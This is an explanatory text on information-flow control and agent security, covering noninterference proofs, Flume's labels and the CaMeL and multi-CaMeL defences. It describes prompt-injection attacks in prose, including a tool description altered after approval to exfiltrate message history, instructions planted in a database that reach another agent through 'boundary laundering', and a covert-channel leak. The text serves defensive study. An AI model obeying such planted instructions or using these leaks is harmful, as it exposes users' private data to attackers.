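A path in a graph shows that data could get from a source to a sink. Proving that a secret has no influence on a public output takes a closer reading of the code, branch by branch. Information-flow types do this. Each variable has a fixed label, and the compiler rejects any program that breaks the rules, without running it. The central rule covers assignment. With S for secret data and U for untrusted data, as before, the compiler accepts x := e only if

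label(e) ∪ pc ⊆ label(x).

Here label(e) is the union of the labels of everything in the expression e. The control label, pc, is the union of the labels of all conditions that determine whether the line runs.

Suppose `salary` has the label {S} and `report` has the label { }. Outside any branch, `pc` is { }, so the assignment `report := salary` requires {S} ⊆ { }. That is false, so the compiler rejects the program.

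The control label, pc, catches implicit flows. The first line of Fenton's program sets the public variable *c* to true if the secret *a* is false. Inside that branch pc is {S}, so the compiler rejects the assignment even though the constant "true" is not itself secret. Unlike a run-time tracker, a compiler also examines the lines that a run would skip.

*Type-Based Enforcement of Non-Interference for Choreographic Programming* (Bertoni, Giallorenzo and Peressotti, 2026) extends the rule to protocols with several participants. A choreography is a single program that sets out a whole protocol, including who sends what to whom, and a compiler derives each participant's program from it. Sending a message counts as an assignment to a variable that belongs to the receiver, so the same rule covers messages and assignments.

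Their example is a password reset. A visitor submits an email address, and the service looks up whether it belongs to an account. The result should stay secret. In the faulty version, the service replies "email sent" if the account exists and "unknown user" if it doesn't, so anyone can find out whether an address has an account. Neither reply contains secret data, but the service sends each one inside a branch that depends on the secret result. The control label is therefore {S}, and the type system rejects a message to the visitor's public variable. In the corrected version, only the message to the mailer depends on the lookup, and the visitor gets the same reply either way. This version passes as long as the mailer's copy of the address has the label {S}.

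Bertoni and colleagues prove noninterference for every choreography that passes the check, which means that if two runs start with the same public values and both finish, they end with the same public values. The theorem doesn't cover what an observer could learn from how long a run takes or whether it finishes.

The theorem also assumes that an expression always gives the same value for the same inputs. A language model that samples its words violates this assumption unless the analysis treats the random choices as another input. The protocol language has no instruction for adding a participant, so if a new agent joins, someone has to write it into the protocol, label its variables and run the check again.

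### The order of actions

Other protocol checks deal with what an agent may do next. *Concordat* (Sikaroudi, 2026) presents a Python library that lets the developer specify when each tool is available during a job. A refund agent, for example, must verify the customer's identity, propose a refund, and then wait for a person to approve or reject it. When the developer defines the agent, the library checks that the agent can reach every stage and can finish from any stage. It also rejects a modified version of the agent that takes a shortcut, such as issuing an instant refund without approval.

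Checking the definition cannot make a language model follow the protocol, so the library enforces the protocol during the run. At each turn, it offers the model only the tools the protocol allows at that stage and blocks any other call before it takes effect.

Sikaroudi tested this on 50 airline tasks from τ-bench, a benchmark with simulated customers. The airline's policy requires an explicit "yes" before any change to a booking. Sikaroudi had the customers resist the first request for confirmation with replies like "just do it and stop asking". The benchmark's standard agent made changes without a yes in 13 of 50 tasks with GPT-4.1, and in 29 of 128 runs with Claude Haiku 5.5. The Concordat agent never made a change without a yes, and it completed about as many tasks as the standard agent.

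That zero follows from the design, because the same keyword test for "yes" both unlocked the tools and scored the result. The standard agent's failures are more informative. In the first set of runs with Haiku, 8 of the 13 tasks with an unconfirmed change still got full marks because the final booking matched the benchmark's expected result.

The order of actions and secrecy are separate properties. The refund agent could go through its stages in the right order and still put another customer's address in a message, because the library attaches no secrecy labels to data. An agent that leaks nothing may still pay a refund that nobody approved.

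### Why prediction fails when systems grow

Every check so far has started from a fixed set of participants and tools. Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman (1976), in *Protection in operating systems*, showed what can go wrong when the set grows. They modelled a computer's access rules as a table with a row for each subject (a user or program) and a column for each object. Each cell lists the subject's rights over the object. A fixed list of commands can change the table. Each command tests for certain rights and, if they are present, adds or removes rights, or creates or deletes subjects and objects. They asked whether a right can leak, meaning that some sequence of commands would put it in a cell where it wasn't before.

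If no command can create new subjects or objects, a program can always determine whether the leak can happen. The table can't grow, so there are only finitely many ways to fill it. With three subjects, four objects and two rights, it has 24 yes-or-no entries, which gives about 17 million possible tables. The program can start from the current table, try every command on every table it reaches, and check each result for the leak.

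When commands can create subjects and objects, the table can grow without limit, so the proof can use it as the memory of a Turing machine, the standard mathematical model of a computer. Each subject stands for one cell on the machine's tape, and one right links each subject to the next in order. Other rights record the symbol in each cell, the machine's position and its current state. The commands imitate the machine's steps, and creating a subject adds a cell to the tape. The machine's halting state is also a right, which appears in the table only if the machine halts. A method that could always decide whether a right leaks could therefore also decide whether any given program halts, which Turing proved impossible in 1936.

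In an agent system, starting a sub-agent adds a row and connecting a tool adds a column. Some systems that grow this way can still be analyzed. The textbook chapter *Foundational Results* cites one that Jones, Lipton and Snyder presented in the same year, where finding the answer takes time proportional to the system's size. Their rules allowed creation but restricted how rights could spread. An agent platform with a few simple rules for passing on authority might likewise allow a proof that is impossible for platforms in general.

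David, Guarnieri and Gervais (2026), in *Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems*, prove a similar limit for tools that an agent acquires while it works. Their contracts are for agents that test a client's systems for weaknesses, and specify which machines the agent may contact, which kinds of action it may take, how many requests it may make and where its findings may go. Ideally, an inspector program would examine each new tool beforehand and admit it only if the tool would never attempt a forbidden action.

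If such an inspector were always right, it could solve the halting problem, which is undecidable. For any program, one can build a tool that runs the program and attempts a forbidden action if the program finishes. The inspector would admit this tool if the program never finishes and reject it otherwise. David and colleagues give this construction in prose, while the computer-checked version of the theorem takes the link to an undecidable problem as a premise. An inspector that rejects every bad tool can still be useful, even if it also rejects some good ones.

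The two results have different causes. Capping the number of agents and tools would make the 1976 question decidable, but it wouldn't help the inspector, which has to predict what a single tool's code will do.

### What a monitor needs

A run-time monitor avoids both limits because it decides about each action when a tool attempts it, without having to predict anything. Under the contracts of David and colleagues, the monitor checks whether the target is in scope, whether the contract allows this kind of action, whether enough of the budget remains, and whether any data that the action declares may go to its destination. They prove that the actions it allows always satisfy the contract, even if an attacker controls the model.

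The proof depends on mediation, meaning that the monitor controls every action a tool takes. The theorem no longer applies if a new tool can load code into the operating system's kernel or use a channel that the monitor doesn't watch. David and colleagues therefore require new tools to run in a sandbox that enforces mediation. They also show that the guarantee holds after the system changes, as long as each change preserves mediation. Checking mediation is a smaller task than checking the whole graph, but whoever deploys the system has to do it for every change.

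A tool on someone else's server can't meet this condition in full, because no sandbox on the user's machine contains it. The monitor can observe only the request and the reply, so it can't detect whether the server then emails the contents to a stranger. The safe course is to treat the request itself as a disclosure to whoever runs the server, and to block it if the data's label doesn't allow that disclosure.

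A monitor is also limited because it can't check steps that haven't happened yet. Ray (2026), in *What Can Be Enforced?*, considers the rule that a confirmation must eventually follow every payment. If the monitor allows a payment, the payment can't be undone if the confirmation never comes, but if it blocks the payment, it also stops runs that would have obeyed the rule. Noninterference is similarly hard to enforce because it compares two runs and the monitor observes only one. A monitor can guarantee noninterference only by being stricter than necessary, as in the proof by Garby and colleagues, which also covers agents that write their own code.

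### A tool that changes after approval

An MCP server can notify a client that its list of tools has changed, and the client then has to fetch the list again to find out what is different. If the server is honest, this notification would be a natural signal to repeat an advance check, but a malicious server can change its tools without sending it.

In April 2025 the AI security company Invariant Labs demonstrated an attack that didn't need the notification. The company built a server with one harmless tool, which returned a random fact of the day. After the user had approved the tool, the server gave it a new description the next time it started. This description included instructions about a different tool, which sent WhatsApp messages through a separate, legitimate server. An agent connected to both servers followed these instructions and sent the user's message history to the attacker's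 number. The description was enough because clients put the descriptions of all connected tools into the model's context.

The attack added a flow of information from the fact server to the message tool through the model's context. Repeating a structural check would not have caught this change, because Agentproof's graph records the names of tools and the order of steps, and both stayed the same.

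A client could do better by storing a fingerprint of each tool definition the user approves and refusing the tool if the fingerprint no longer matches. This would have stopped the Invariant Labs server, but it would not stop a server that keeps the definition and changes the code behind it, because the client never sees that code.

Fingerprints would also make label checks more practical. A provider's description is text from outside, so a strict scheme would give it the mark U, and connecting any third-party server would taint the context from the start. To avoid this, the deployer would have to read and endorse each description. A fingerprint limits the endorsement to the text the deployer read.

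### Checking each new plan

Some agents write a new plan for each request, so software can check each plan before the agent calls any tool. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) does this for CaMeL, whose planning model writes each plan as a short program in restricted Python. It converts the program into a state machine that includes both branches of every condition and any number of repetitions of a loop. It marks each value with its origin, and a value made from several others gets the least trusted of their origins. A model checker, which explores every state the machine can reach, then tests the plan against a set of rules.

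In the paper's example, the plan reads the messages in a chat channel, has the quarantined model extract Bob's email address from them, and sends a message to that address. One rule requires a trusted recipient for every direct message. In the notation of temporal logic, it reads

AG(call_send_direct_message ⇒ recipient_trusted),

where AG means "in every state on every path". The address comes from messages that other people wrote, so the plan fails. The model checker returns the sequence of steps that leads to the violation, and the planning model gets a description of it and tries again. A new plan can pass only if the address comes from somewhere trusted, such as the user's own request. Because no tool has run yet, the agent has nothing to undo.

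With the whole plan available, the software can also check rules about what must eventually happen, which a monitor that only allows or blocks actions can't enforce. For example, a rule might require the agent to resolve or escalate every security ticket it opens. Nikolaou and colleagues wrote seven unsafe plans for an agent on a security team, each of which broke a different rule. CaMeLoT caught all seven, and a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. This gap was expected because they had designed the rules to go beyond what CaMeL can express.

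Some facts, such as who can read a shared file at a given moment, exist only during the run. CaMeLoT could check 22 of CaMeL's 28 policies for AgentDojo in advance, and CaMeL still applies its own checks to every call. On AgentDojo's 97 ordinary tasks, 22 plans failed to do what the user wanted under both systems. The two systems agreed on 59 of the other 75.

The rules also have to be right. CaMeLoT can derive some of them from the user's request by having a language model choose from a fixed set of rule types. It identified the required actions exactly in 85 of the 97 tasks. Translation is much less reliable when the model isn't limited to a fixed set. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026), a review of 38 studies, calls specification the bottleneck and cites a benchmark on which only 25 to 34 percent of model-written translations into a formal planning language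 had the right meaning.

A check at deployment may be months old when a tool changes. CaMeLoT checks every plan, which shortens the time a change can go unnoticed. But it treats each tool as a black box with a name and arguments, so a plan that calls a redefined tool, such as the weekly report tool, would still pass.

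## Flume: labels for processes that come and go

Operating systems had the problem of changing connections long before agents did. Programs start and stop constantly, and any of them can open files, start more programs and exchange messages with those already running, so nobody can draw the communication graph in advance. *Information Flow Control for Standard OS Abstractions* (Krohn, Yip and colleagues, 2007) describes Flume, a layer on top of Linux that enforces information flow control under these conditions.

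Flume attaches labels to processes. A process is a running program with its own memory, which other programs can't read unless the operating system lets them. A process that Flume confines can't make most requests to Linux directly and has to send them to a reference monitor, a trusted program that checks the labels before carrying out each request for the process. Flume's label checks depend on requests going through this monitor.

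### Tags and the rights to change them

Suppose Bob downloads a text editor that might secretly post his files on a website. Auditing the editor and all its libraries would take too long, so one of Bob's own processes creates a tag, *b*, to mark his private data. A tag is a token with no built-in meaning. Any process can create one, whereas in older military systems only a security officer could.

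Every process *p* has two sets of tags, a secrecy label S_p and an integrity label I_p. If the tag *b* is in S_p, Flume treats *p* as having seen Bob's private data. A tag in I_p means that every input so far was endorsed, unlike the mark U in the earlier examples, which means that something untrusted has got in. A result made from two inputs therefore keeps the secrecy tags of both but only the integrity tags they share.

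Each tag comes with two rights. The right *b*+ lets a process add *b* to its labels, and *b*− lets it remove *b*. The process that creates the tag gets both rights and can give one of them to everyone. Bob's process gives everyone *b*+ and keeps *b*−. Any program can then read Bob's files after adding *b* to its secrecy label, but it can't remove the tag. If Bob's process kept *b*+ as well, other programs couldn't read the files. Integrity tags usually reverse this arrangement, so any process can remove the tag but only a trusted certifier can add it.

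Flume calls these rights capabilities. They are close to capabilities in Hardy's sense, because a process can't forge them but can pass them to another process.

A process can change a label from L to L′ only if it holds the right for every tag it adds or removes. With O_p as the set of rights that *p* holds, the rule is

{L′ − L}+ ∪ {L − L′}− ⊆ O_p.

For example, Bob wants to suggest meeting times to Alice without showing her the rest of his calendar. Alice's calendar has the tag *a* and Bob's has *b*. Bob starts a process with the secrecy label {a,b} and the right *b*−. The process reads both calendars and works out when both people are free. It then changes its label to {a}, which the rule allows because the only tag it removes is *b*, and writes the suggested times to a file labeled {a}. Alice can release that file, but Bob can't, because the file also contains information about Alice's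 calendar.

### The rule for messages

In the basic case, *p* can send a message to *q* only if

S_p ⊆ S_q and I_q ⊆ I_p.

The receiver of a message must already have all of the sender's secrecy tags, and the sender must have all of the receiver's integrity tags. Flume treats files as processes whose labels never change, so reading a file counts as sending a message from the file to the reader. It treats the network, the user's screen and anything else outside its control as processes with empty labels.

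The integrity half of the rule can protect a sensitive file such as a computer's startup script. Suppose the script has the integrity label {v}, where *v* marks vendor-certified software. Only an editor with *v* can write to it. If that editor tries to load an uncertified plug-in, the check {v} ⊆ { } fails. The editor can give up *v* and load the plug-in, but then it can no longer change the script, and it can't get *v* back by itself.

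The full rule makes an exception for processes that hold both rights to a tag. Such a process could change its label, exchange the message and change the label back, so Flume's model lets it skip those steps. If D_p is the set of tags for which *p* holds both rights, the message is safe when

S_p − D_p ⊆ S_q ∪ D_q and I_q − D_q ⊆ I_p ∪ D_p.

### A program that arrives midway

Suppose Bob's editor is running with the secrecy label {b} when a backup program starts. The backup program was installed after Bob opened the editor. Its labels are empty, and its only right to Bob's tag is *b*+, which everyone has. Bob's shell, the program he types commands into, has an empty secrecy label and both rights to the tag.

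| What happens | What Flume checks | Result |
|---|---|---|
| The editor sends text to the backup program | {b} ⊆ { } | Dropped |
| The backup program adds *b* to its secrecy label | Does it hold *b*+? | Allowed |
| The editor sends the text again | {b} ⊆ {b} | Delivered |
| The backup program tries to upload the text | {b} ⊆ { } | Blocked |
| It tries to start a helper with an empty label | Does it hold *b*−? | Blocked |
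| It sends the text to Bob's shell | {b} ⊆ { } ∪ {b} | Delivered |

By default, a new process gets the labels of the process that started it. The parent can choose different labels only if it could have made the same change to its own, so the backup program can't use a helper to get rid of *b*. If the backup program is already connected to the network when it asks to add *b*, the monitor refuses the change, because no process may hold both an open channel to the outside and secrets it has no right to release.

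For each message, the monitor looked only at the labels and rights of the two processes involved. This is enough because the subset relation is transitive, as Denning required of any flow relation. A later version of *Making Information Flow Explicit in HiStar*, a paper on a related operating system, points out that transitivity makes it unnecessary to trace the possible routes between two processes.

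The argument still holds when new processes start. A process that has received Bob's data always has the tag *b*, unless a holder of *b*− removed the tag or released the data. A new process either has none of Bob's data or starts with its parent's label, and each later message preserves this property.

Bob still has to know who holds *b*−, because any program with that right can release his data. During a run, a holder can pass the right to any process it can communicate with, so the safest choice is to give it only to small programs that someone has checked. *Making Information Flow Explicit in HiStar* (Zeldovich, Boyd-Wickizer and colleagues, 2006) describes how HiStar confined a virus scanner of more than 40,000 lines. The scanner could start whatever helper programs it needed, but only a 110-line wrapper could report its results to the user. As long as the wrapper was correct, a compromised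 scanner couldn't send out the files it read.

### How automatic labels leak secrets

The backup program had to add *b* before the editor's text could reach it, which is inconvenient because a program has to know which tags it will need. Asbestos, an earlier operating system built by several of the same researchers, didn't require programs to add tags before receiving a message. It gave each process a send label, which recorded the secrets the process had seen, and a receive label, which limited what it could receive (Efstathopoulos, Krohn and colleagues, 2005, *Labels and Event Processes in the Asbestos Operating System*). If a message was within the receiver's limit, Asbestos delivered it and raised the receiver's send label to the join of the two processes' send labels. A label that rises this way is called a floating label.

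Floating labels can reveal secrets. *Noninterference for a Practical DIFC-Based Operating System* (Krohn and Tromer, 2009) shows how, using the two-bit secret 01. Process *p* has the secret and the label {t}. A cooperating process *q* has an empty label and is meant to obtain the secret without acquiring *t*.

1. *q* writes down 00 as its first guess and starts two helpers with empty labels, one for each bit.
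2. *p* sends a message to the helper for each bit that is 0. The first helper receives one, and its label rises to {t}. The second receives nothing, so its label stays empty.
3. After an agreed time, each helper that has received nothing sends a 1 to *q*. Only the second helper does this, so *q* changes its second bit to 1.

Now *q* has 01, and its label is still empty because no message containing secret data reached it. The second helper could report a 1 because *p* had sent it nothing, just as Fenton's program leaks a secret through an assignment that it skips. With *n* helpers, *p* can leak *n* bits in each waiting period. Asbestos could create lightweight processes so quickly that Krohn and Tromer estimated the leak could reach kilobits per second.

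Efstathopoulos and colleagues described a version of this leak in which two processes send regular signals to a third, and the secret determines which of the two stops. They considered such leaks inherent in any system that checks changing labels at run time, and suggested limiting how many processes a program could start.

HiStar closed this channel by changing a thread's label only when the thread requests it, and Flume does the same. Under Flume, each helper in the attack has to choose its label before it can receive the message from *p*. If it adds *t*, it can receive the message but can't write to *q*. If it keeps an empty label, it never receives the message and sends a 1 whatever the secret is. Either way, *q* gets no information about the secret.

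Explicit labels make more work for the programmer. When Flume drops a message, it doesn't notify the sender or the receiver, because an error report could reveal something about the other process's label. These silent failures make programs hard to debug. Flume reduces the problem by giving each connection its own labels, which a process can set in advance. Flume can safely report an error in these settings because the error depends only on the process's own labels and rights.

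A file's name, or the fact that it exists, can also leak a secret, so a process that has read a secret can't create files in a public directory. The process has to create any such files before it reads anything private, leaving them empty and giving them restrictive labels.

Requiring a process to change its own label does not prevent label creep. A server that handles requests from many users would soon collect all their tags and be unable to answer any of them. Asbestos avoided this by keeping each user's data and labels in a separate compartment of the server, called an event process. In a test with a simple web service, each stored session needed about 1.5 memory pages (6 kilobytes).

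### What the proof covers

Krohn and Tromer proved noninterference for a mathematical model of Flume. They considered pairs of histories that differ only in the actions of processes that have a secret tag *t* but lack *t*−, the right to remove it. Processes with neither *t* nor *t*− must be able to do exactly the same things after either history. The model still allows deliberate declassification, because a process that holds *t*− can pass secret data to them.

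The theorem covers any programs that users run. In the model, these programs can start other processes, create tags, change their labels and pass on rights. The proof therefore still holds when a new process joins, unlike a proof about a fixed workflow.

Process identifiers can also leak information. If the system numbered processes in order, a public process could start a child and note its number. A secret process could then start *k* processes, and the public process could work out *k* from the number of its next child. Krohn and Tromer's model instead draws identifiers at random from a huge range, with separate pools for processes with different labels. An attacker might still guess one, so they prove that noninterference holds with a probability of at least 1 − 2^−ε, where the administrator chooses ε. For a system that performs at most 2^80 operations, 320-bit identifiers keep the chance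 of failure below 2^−100.

The proof applies to the model, and nobody had verified that Flume's code matched the model. The model also leaves out timing and hardware, so a process might still signal a secret by how heavily it uses the processor or the disk. Zeldovich and colleagues had the same problem with HiStar and wrote that they didn't know how to solve it, because many network services must respond quickly and an outsider can measure the delays.

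### A wiki that starts a process for every request

To test Flume on real software, Krohn and colleagues adapted MoinMoin, a wiki program with about 91,000 lines of code. The original code checked in 41 places whether a user could read a page, and forgetting one check could expose a private page. In the Flume version, a small launcher starts a new process for each request and sets its labels according to who is logged in. Only the launcher can release the finished page to the user's browser, so the policy stays in one place even though the processes change with every request.

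The adaptation took about 1,000 lines of changes to MoinMoin and 1,000 new lines for the launcher. The code still had two known bugs that let users bypass the permission checks, but Flume kept them from revealing private data. The work also exposed an undocumented leak. In the original wiki, Bob could try to create a page called `ReasonsToFireBob` and learn from the failure that it already existed.

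Protection slowed the wiki from 33.2 page views per second to 18.8, a drop of 43 percent, and from 16.9 edits per second to 11.1, a drop of 34 percent. Page load time rose from 117 to 156 milliseconds. Most of this delay came from opening and looking up files, since a single page view sent 753 requests to the monitor. Hit counters and the search index also stopped working because they share files between users, which Flume treats as an attempted leak. The researchers didn't have time to write the declassifiers that would have restored these features.

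Most of Flume's message rule would work for language-model agents. The software that runs them could check the labels of both agents on every message, start each sub-agent with its parent's label, and apply the same rule to an agent it has just discovered. The checks would add little delay, because they take microseconds and a model call usually takes seconds. The boundary between processes is harder to reproduce. Flume gives a whole process one label, but a programmer can put Alice's and Bob's data in separate processes, whose memory the operating system keeps apart. *Laminar*, another system of this kind, can label separate pieces of data within one program. A model's context has no such partitions, so the agent system FIDES keeps one label for everything its planner has seen. If that label rises automatically when a tool result arrives, cooperating agents could in principle leak data the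 same way as the helpers in Asbestos. An agent that reads untrusted text also shouldn't hold a right like *b*−, because a planted instruction could persuade it to release the data.

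## CaMeL, and why protecting each agent did not protect the group

A model's context has no partitions, so CaMeL keeps untrusted text away from the model that chooses the actions. Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues presented the design in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). They kept Willison's planning and quarantined models, but had the planning model write the whole job as a short program before any tool ran.

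CaMeL gives a single agent control-flow integrity. A group of such agents can still lack it, because one agent's data can become the next agent's instructions.

### A program written before the data arrives

Suppose a user asks an agent to pay the December bill, which is in a file. The planning model gets the request and the descriptions of the available tools, and writes a program like this:

```
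bill = read_file("december.txt")
payee = quarantined_model("Find the account number", bill)
amount = quarantined_model("Find the amount due", bill)
send_money(payee, amount)
```

Ordinary software called an interpreter then runs the program.

1. It reads the file and stores the text as `bill`. The planning model never sees the text.
2. It passes the text to the quarantined model, which has no tools and must answer in a fixed form, such as an account number.
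3. It attaches a provenance tag to each value, recording the value's sources and who may read it. Because the account number came from `bill`, the interpreter also links it to that file.
4. Before calling `send_money`, it runs a policy. As Nikolaou and colleagues describe it, a policy is a Python function that receives the proposed call, its arguments and their tags, and returns "allow" or "deny" with a reason.

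An instruction hidden in the bill can't add a line to this program. The invoice attack doesn't need an extra line, but a policy could stop it by refusing to pay any account number that came from a file strangers can write to. The interpreter can also ask the user to confirm the payment, according to TechSpot.

The record of permitted readers protects secrets. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a policy that stops the agent from emailing a confidential document to someone not permitted to read it. The policy works even if the quarantined model took the recipient's address from a poisoned page.

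People have to write these policies by hand, and Foerster and colleagues know of no automatic way to derive them. Strict policies also block legitimate work. Garby and colleagues report that turning on the policy checks halved the share of AgentDojo's banking tasks that CaMeL completed. They also found that CaMeL's interpreter misses some implicit flows and that a retry loop around it can leak secrets bit by bit.

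### When the program lacks a step

A shop's checkout page may require a code that the shop has just sent by email. An agent that decides each step as it goes can open the mailbox and continue. CaMeL can do this only if the planning model wrote a branch for it in advance.

Tools that appear during the run cause the same difficulty. The planning model chooses from the tools available at the start, so its program never calls a mail tool added halfway through. That is safe, but the agent can't use the new tool until the planning model writes another program.

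Requesting a new program mid-job would undo the protection if that program depended on the checkout page's text, because untrusted text would then influence the plan. Foerster and colleagues consider this a fundamental limit. If a user tells the agent to follow the instructions in an email, the planning model can't list the steps without reading the email.

AgentDojo hardly tests for this. According to *AgentDyn*, only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 user tasks require planning during the run, whereas all 60 of its own do. CaMeL completed none of the 60 with any of the four models in the main comparison, while an undefended agent using GPT-4o completed 53 percent. No attack on CaMeL succeeded, but that is little evidence of security because CaMeL completed no tasks.

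Some of this failure may come from the setup. *AutoDojo* (2026), a later benchmark, left CaMeL out of its tests on these tasks because CaMeL needs extensive policies for each set of tools.

Results are better for agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen, clicking and typing. Foerster and colleagues had the planning model write branches for whatever might appear, such as a cookie notice or a login page. The programs averaged 213 lines and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines and 4 branches for AgentDojo, and about half of their steps were fallbacks that didn't run. The agents kept up to 57 percent of frontier models' performance.

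*Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues, 2026) tested a later version of the design on 361 computer tasks, with up to five attempts at each. Sonnet 5 completed 51.0 percent of them when it could look at the screen before every step, and 38.8 percent when it had to plan ahead.

### Three protected agents and one leak

Schroeder de Witt and colleagues had argued in general terms that individually safe agents can form an unsafe system. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, built such a system from three agents, each protected by its own copy of CaMeL:

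- The orchestrator takes the user's request. It has no tools of its own but can call the other two agents.
- The SQL agent can query a database.
- The notification agent can send emails and Slack messages.

The user asked the orchestrator to send Julie a summary of all job applicants on Slack. The researchers had planted an instruction in the database to email the applicants' data to an outside address. GPT-5.2 served as both the planning model and the quarantined model in every agent. In simplified form, the orchestrator's program was:

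```
info = sql_agent("Get all the data on job applicants")
summary = quarantined_model("Summarise: " + info)
notification_agent("Slack this summary to Julie: " + summary)
```

The SQL agent's planning model wrote a query without seeing the result. The result, including the planted instruction, went back to the orchestrator as the value `info`, which the orchestrator's planning model didn't see either. Both agents therefore ran the same programs they would have run without the attack. The planted instruction was still in the summary, but up to this point it was only part of a value and couldn't add a step to either program.

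The attack got through at the third line of the program, which joins the summary to an English sentence and sends the result to the notification agent as a request. The notification agent treats the orchestrator as its user, and CaMeL treats the user's request as trusted. The notification agent's planning model therefore treated the planted instruction as part of the request. It wrote a program that sent the summary to Julie on Slack and then emailed it to the attacker's address.

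Data that one agent treats as untrusted becomes trusted when it crosses to the next agent, even though each agent follows CaMeL's rules. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering.

The experiment ran without data policies, but a policy in the notification agent would probably not have helped. That agent's planning model had copied the applicants' details into its program as ordinary text, so its interpreter had no record that they came from a private database. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) notes that CaMeL's tags disappear once a value enters a model's conversation. A single CaMeL agent keeps tool results out of its planning model's conversation, but in this group the orchestrator passed a tool result into the conversation of the notification agent's planning model. A policy in the orchestrator could have blocked its call to the notification agent, because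 the orchestrator's interpreter still had a record of where the summary came from.

Protecting each agent does stop attacks that must take over the agent reading the planted text. In an earlier attack called OMNI-Leak, text in a public database made a SQL agent query a private database. Peters-Gill and colleagues repeated the attack five times against CaMeL agents, and it failed every time. The agents still answered all the ordinary questions correctly.

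### Why the guarantee does not compose

Peters-Gill and colleagues also prove that almost any group of agents arranged in a tree has the same weakness. In this arrangement, the user talks only to the agent at the top, each parent calls its children as if they were tools, and each child treats its parent as its user.

A control-flow plan is a program, fixed in advance, that determines every tool call from the results of earlier ones. A system has control-flow integrity if it always follows a plan that depends only on the user's request and other trusted information. Under this definition, tool descriptions count as trusted, so the guarantee doesn't cover a malicious description like the one on Invariant Labs' fact server.

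The claim is that a tree of two or more agents lacks control-flow integrity if any of its tools returns untrusted data, even if every agent has the property on its own. The proof relies on an expressivity assumption about what users can get agents to do:

- For any tool an agent has, some request makes the agent call it and return the result.
- For any two tools an agent has, and any arguments for the first, some request makes the agent call the first with those arguments and then call the second with arguments that depend on the result. The two may be the same tool, and child agents count as tools.

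An agent with a tool that returns untrusted data must have a child or a parent, because the tree has at least two agents.

If the agent has a child, then by the second part of the assumption, some request makes the agent call the tool and then give the child an instruction that depends on the result. For example, a research agent reads a web page and asks a writing agent to draft a reply, so the writing agent's plan depends on the web page.

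**The agent has a parent.** By the first part, some instruction makes the agent call the tool and return the result. By the second part, some request makes the parent give that instruction and then call the agent again with a new instruction that depends on the result. For example, an orchestrator asks a database agent which customers complained this week, then asks it to look up those customers' orders. The database agent's second instruction now contains text from the database.

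The assumption is mild, since an orchestrator's job is to act on what its helpers report. But the claim is only that some request will make the group's plan depend on untrusted data. It doesn't cover how often users make such requests, or how often a model will follow instructions planted in that data.

The result is consistent with Denning's argument that a sequence of safe steps is safe, because one step here is unsafe. The orchestrator loses a value's tag when it makes the value part of a request. Flume avoids this by checking labels on every message.

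### A separate channel for data

Peters-Gill and colleagues' remedy, multi-CaMeL, splits each call to another agent into two parts. The `message` contains instructions in English, which the child's planning model reads. The `variables` contain data, which the planning model doesn't see. The third line of the orchestrator's program becomes:

```
notification_agent(
    message="Slack the summary to Julie",
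    variables={"summary": summary})
```

The notification agent's planning model can then write a program that fetches the value with `get_variable("summary")` and sends it to Julie. The planted instruction is still in the summary and may reach Julie's screen, but it can't add a step to the program that sends an email.

A planning model might still put data in the wrong channel, so the interpreter enforces two rules:

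- **Instruction-channel integrity.** The message must not depend on any tool output.
- **Preserved provenance.** Values in the variables keep their tags when they pass from one agent to another.

The first rule alone gives the whole tree control-flow integrity. Each child's program depends only on trusted instructions, so one can in principle replace every call to a child with that child's program, and do the same for the child's own calls. The result is one large plan that depends only on the user's request and other trusted information.

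The second rule lets data policies work across the group. The notification agent's interpreter would have a record that the summary came from the applicant database, so a policy there could block sending it to an outsider. The current software misses the same implicit flows as CaMeL, so it could break the first rule in some programs, but it avoids the retry leak because it doesn't retry.

In one benchmark task, a user asks the agents to send Dora and Eve feedback on their websites, which both contain a planted note with instructions to send Alice a link. With individual CaMeL and Gemini 2.5 Pro, the orchestrator pasted the text of Dora's page into its request to the Slack agent, which sent Alice the link before it messaged Dora. With multi-CaMeL and a different planted note, the Slack agent received only an instruction to send the message stored in the variables, and the attack failed.

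However, the feedback in the second run was flawed because the planning model wrote it, including its praise for Dora's "clean design", before the agent opened either site. Peters-Gill and colleagues count the task as completed.

### Results on two benchmarks

To measure the effect, Peters-Gill and colleagues built MultiAgentDojo, which divides AgentDojo's tools among two to four specialised agents under an orchestrator. The office workspace, for example, has separate agents for email, the calendar and files. Dividing the tools changed each model's success rate on ordinary tasks by at most about five percentage points. They ran 949 attacked instances for each model and configuration.

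| Model | No CaMeL | Individual CaMeL | Multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Average attack success | 12.9% | 0.2% | 0.0% |

The 0.2 percent rate for individual CaMeL amounts to about nine successful attacks in 4,745 runs, all of them by boundary laundering, as expected from the proof. The low rate doesn't show that boundary laundering is rare in practice, because the planted texts came from a benchmark for single agents. An attacker who knew the system could write text meant to be passed on, as Liang and colleagues did with their nested instructions.

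GPT-5.5 resisted every attack even without CaMeL, so its results can't show whether either defence works. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn against concluding that the model is immune to attacks in general, because a large public competition found successful attacks on every frontier model it tested.

Fable 5 refused 52 of the 97 ordinary tasks, possibly because it associated the benchmark's setting with attacks. If it also refused attacked tasks, those refusals would lower its attack success rate regardless of the defence.

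The researchers measured the loss in completed work on MultiAgentDojo and on AssetOpsBench, where an orchestrator delegates industrial maintenance tasks to four specialised agents. They removed 29 of the 141 AssetOpsBench tasks because the data they needed didn't exist. A language model judged the remaining 112.

| Model | No CaMeL | Individual CaMeL | Multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 88.4% | 67.0% | 67.9% |
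| GPT-5.5 | 87.5% | 82.1% | 79.5% |
| GPT-4.1 | 81.2% | 64.3% | 48.2% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 75.9% | 55.4% | 50.9% |
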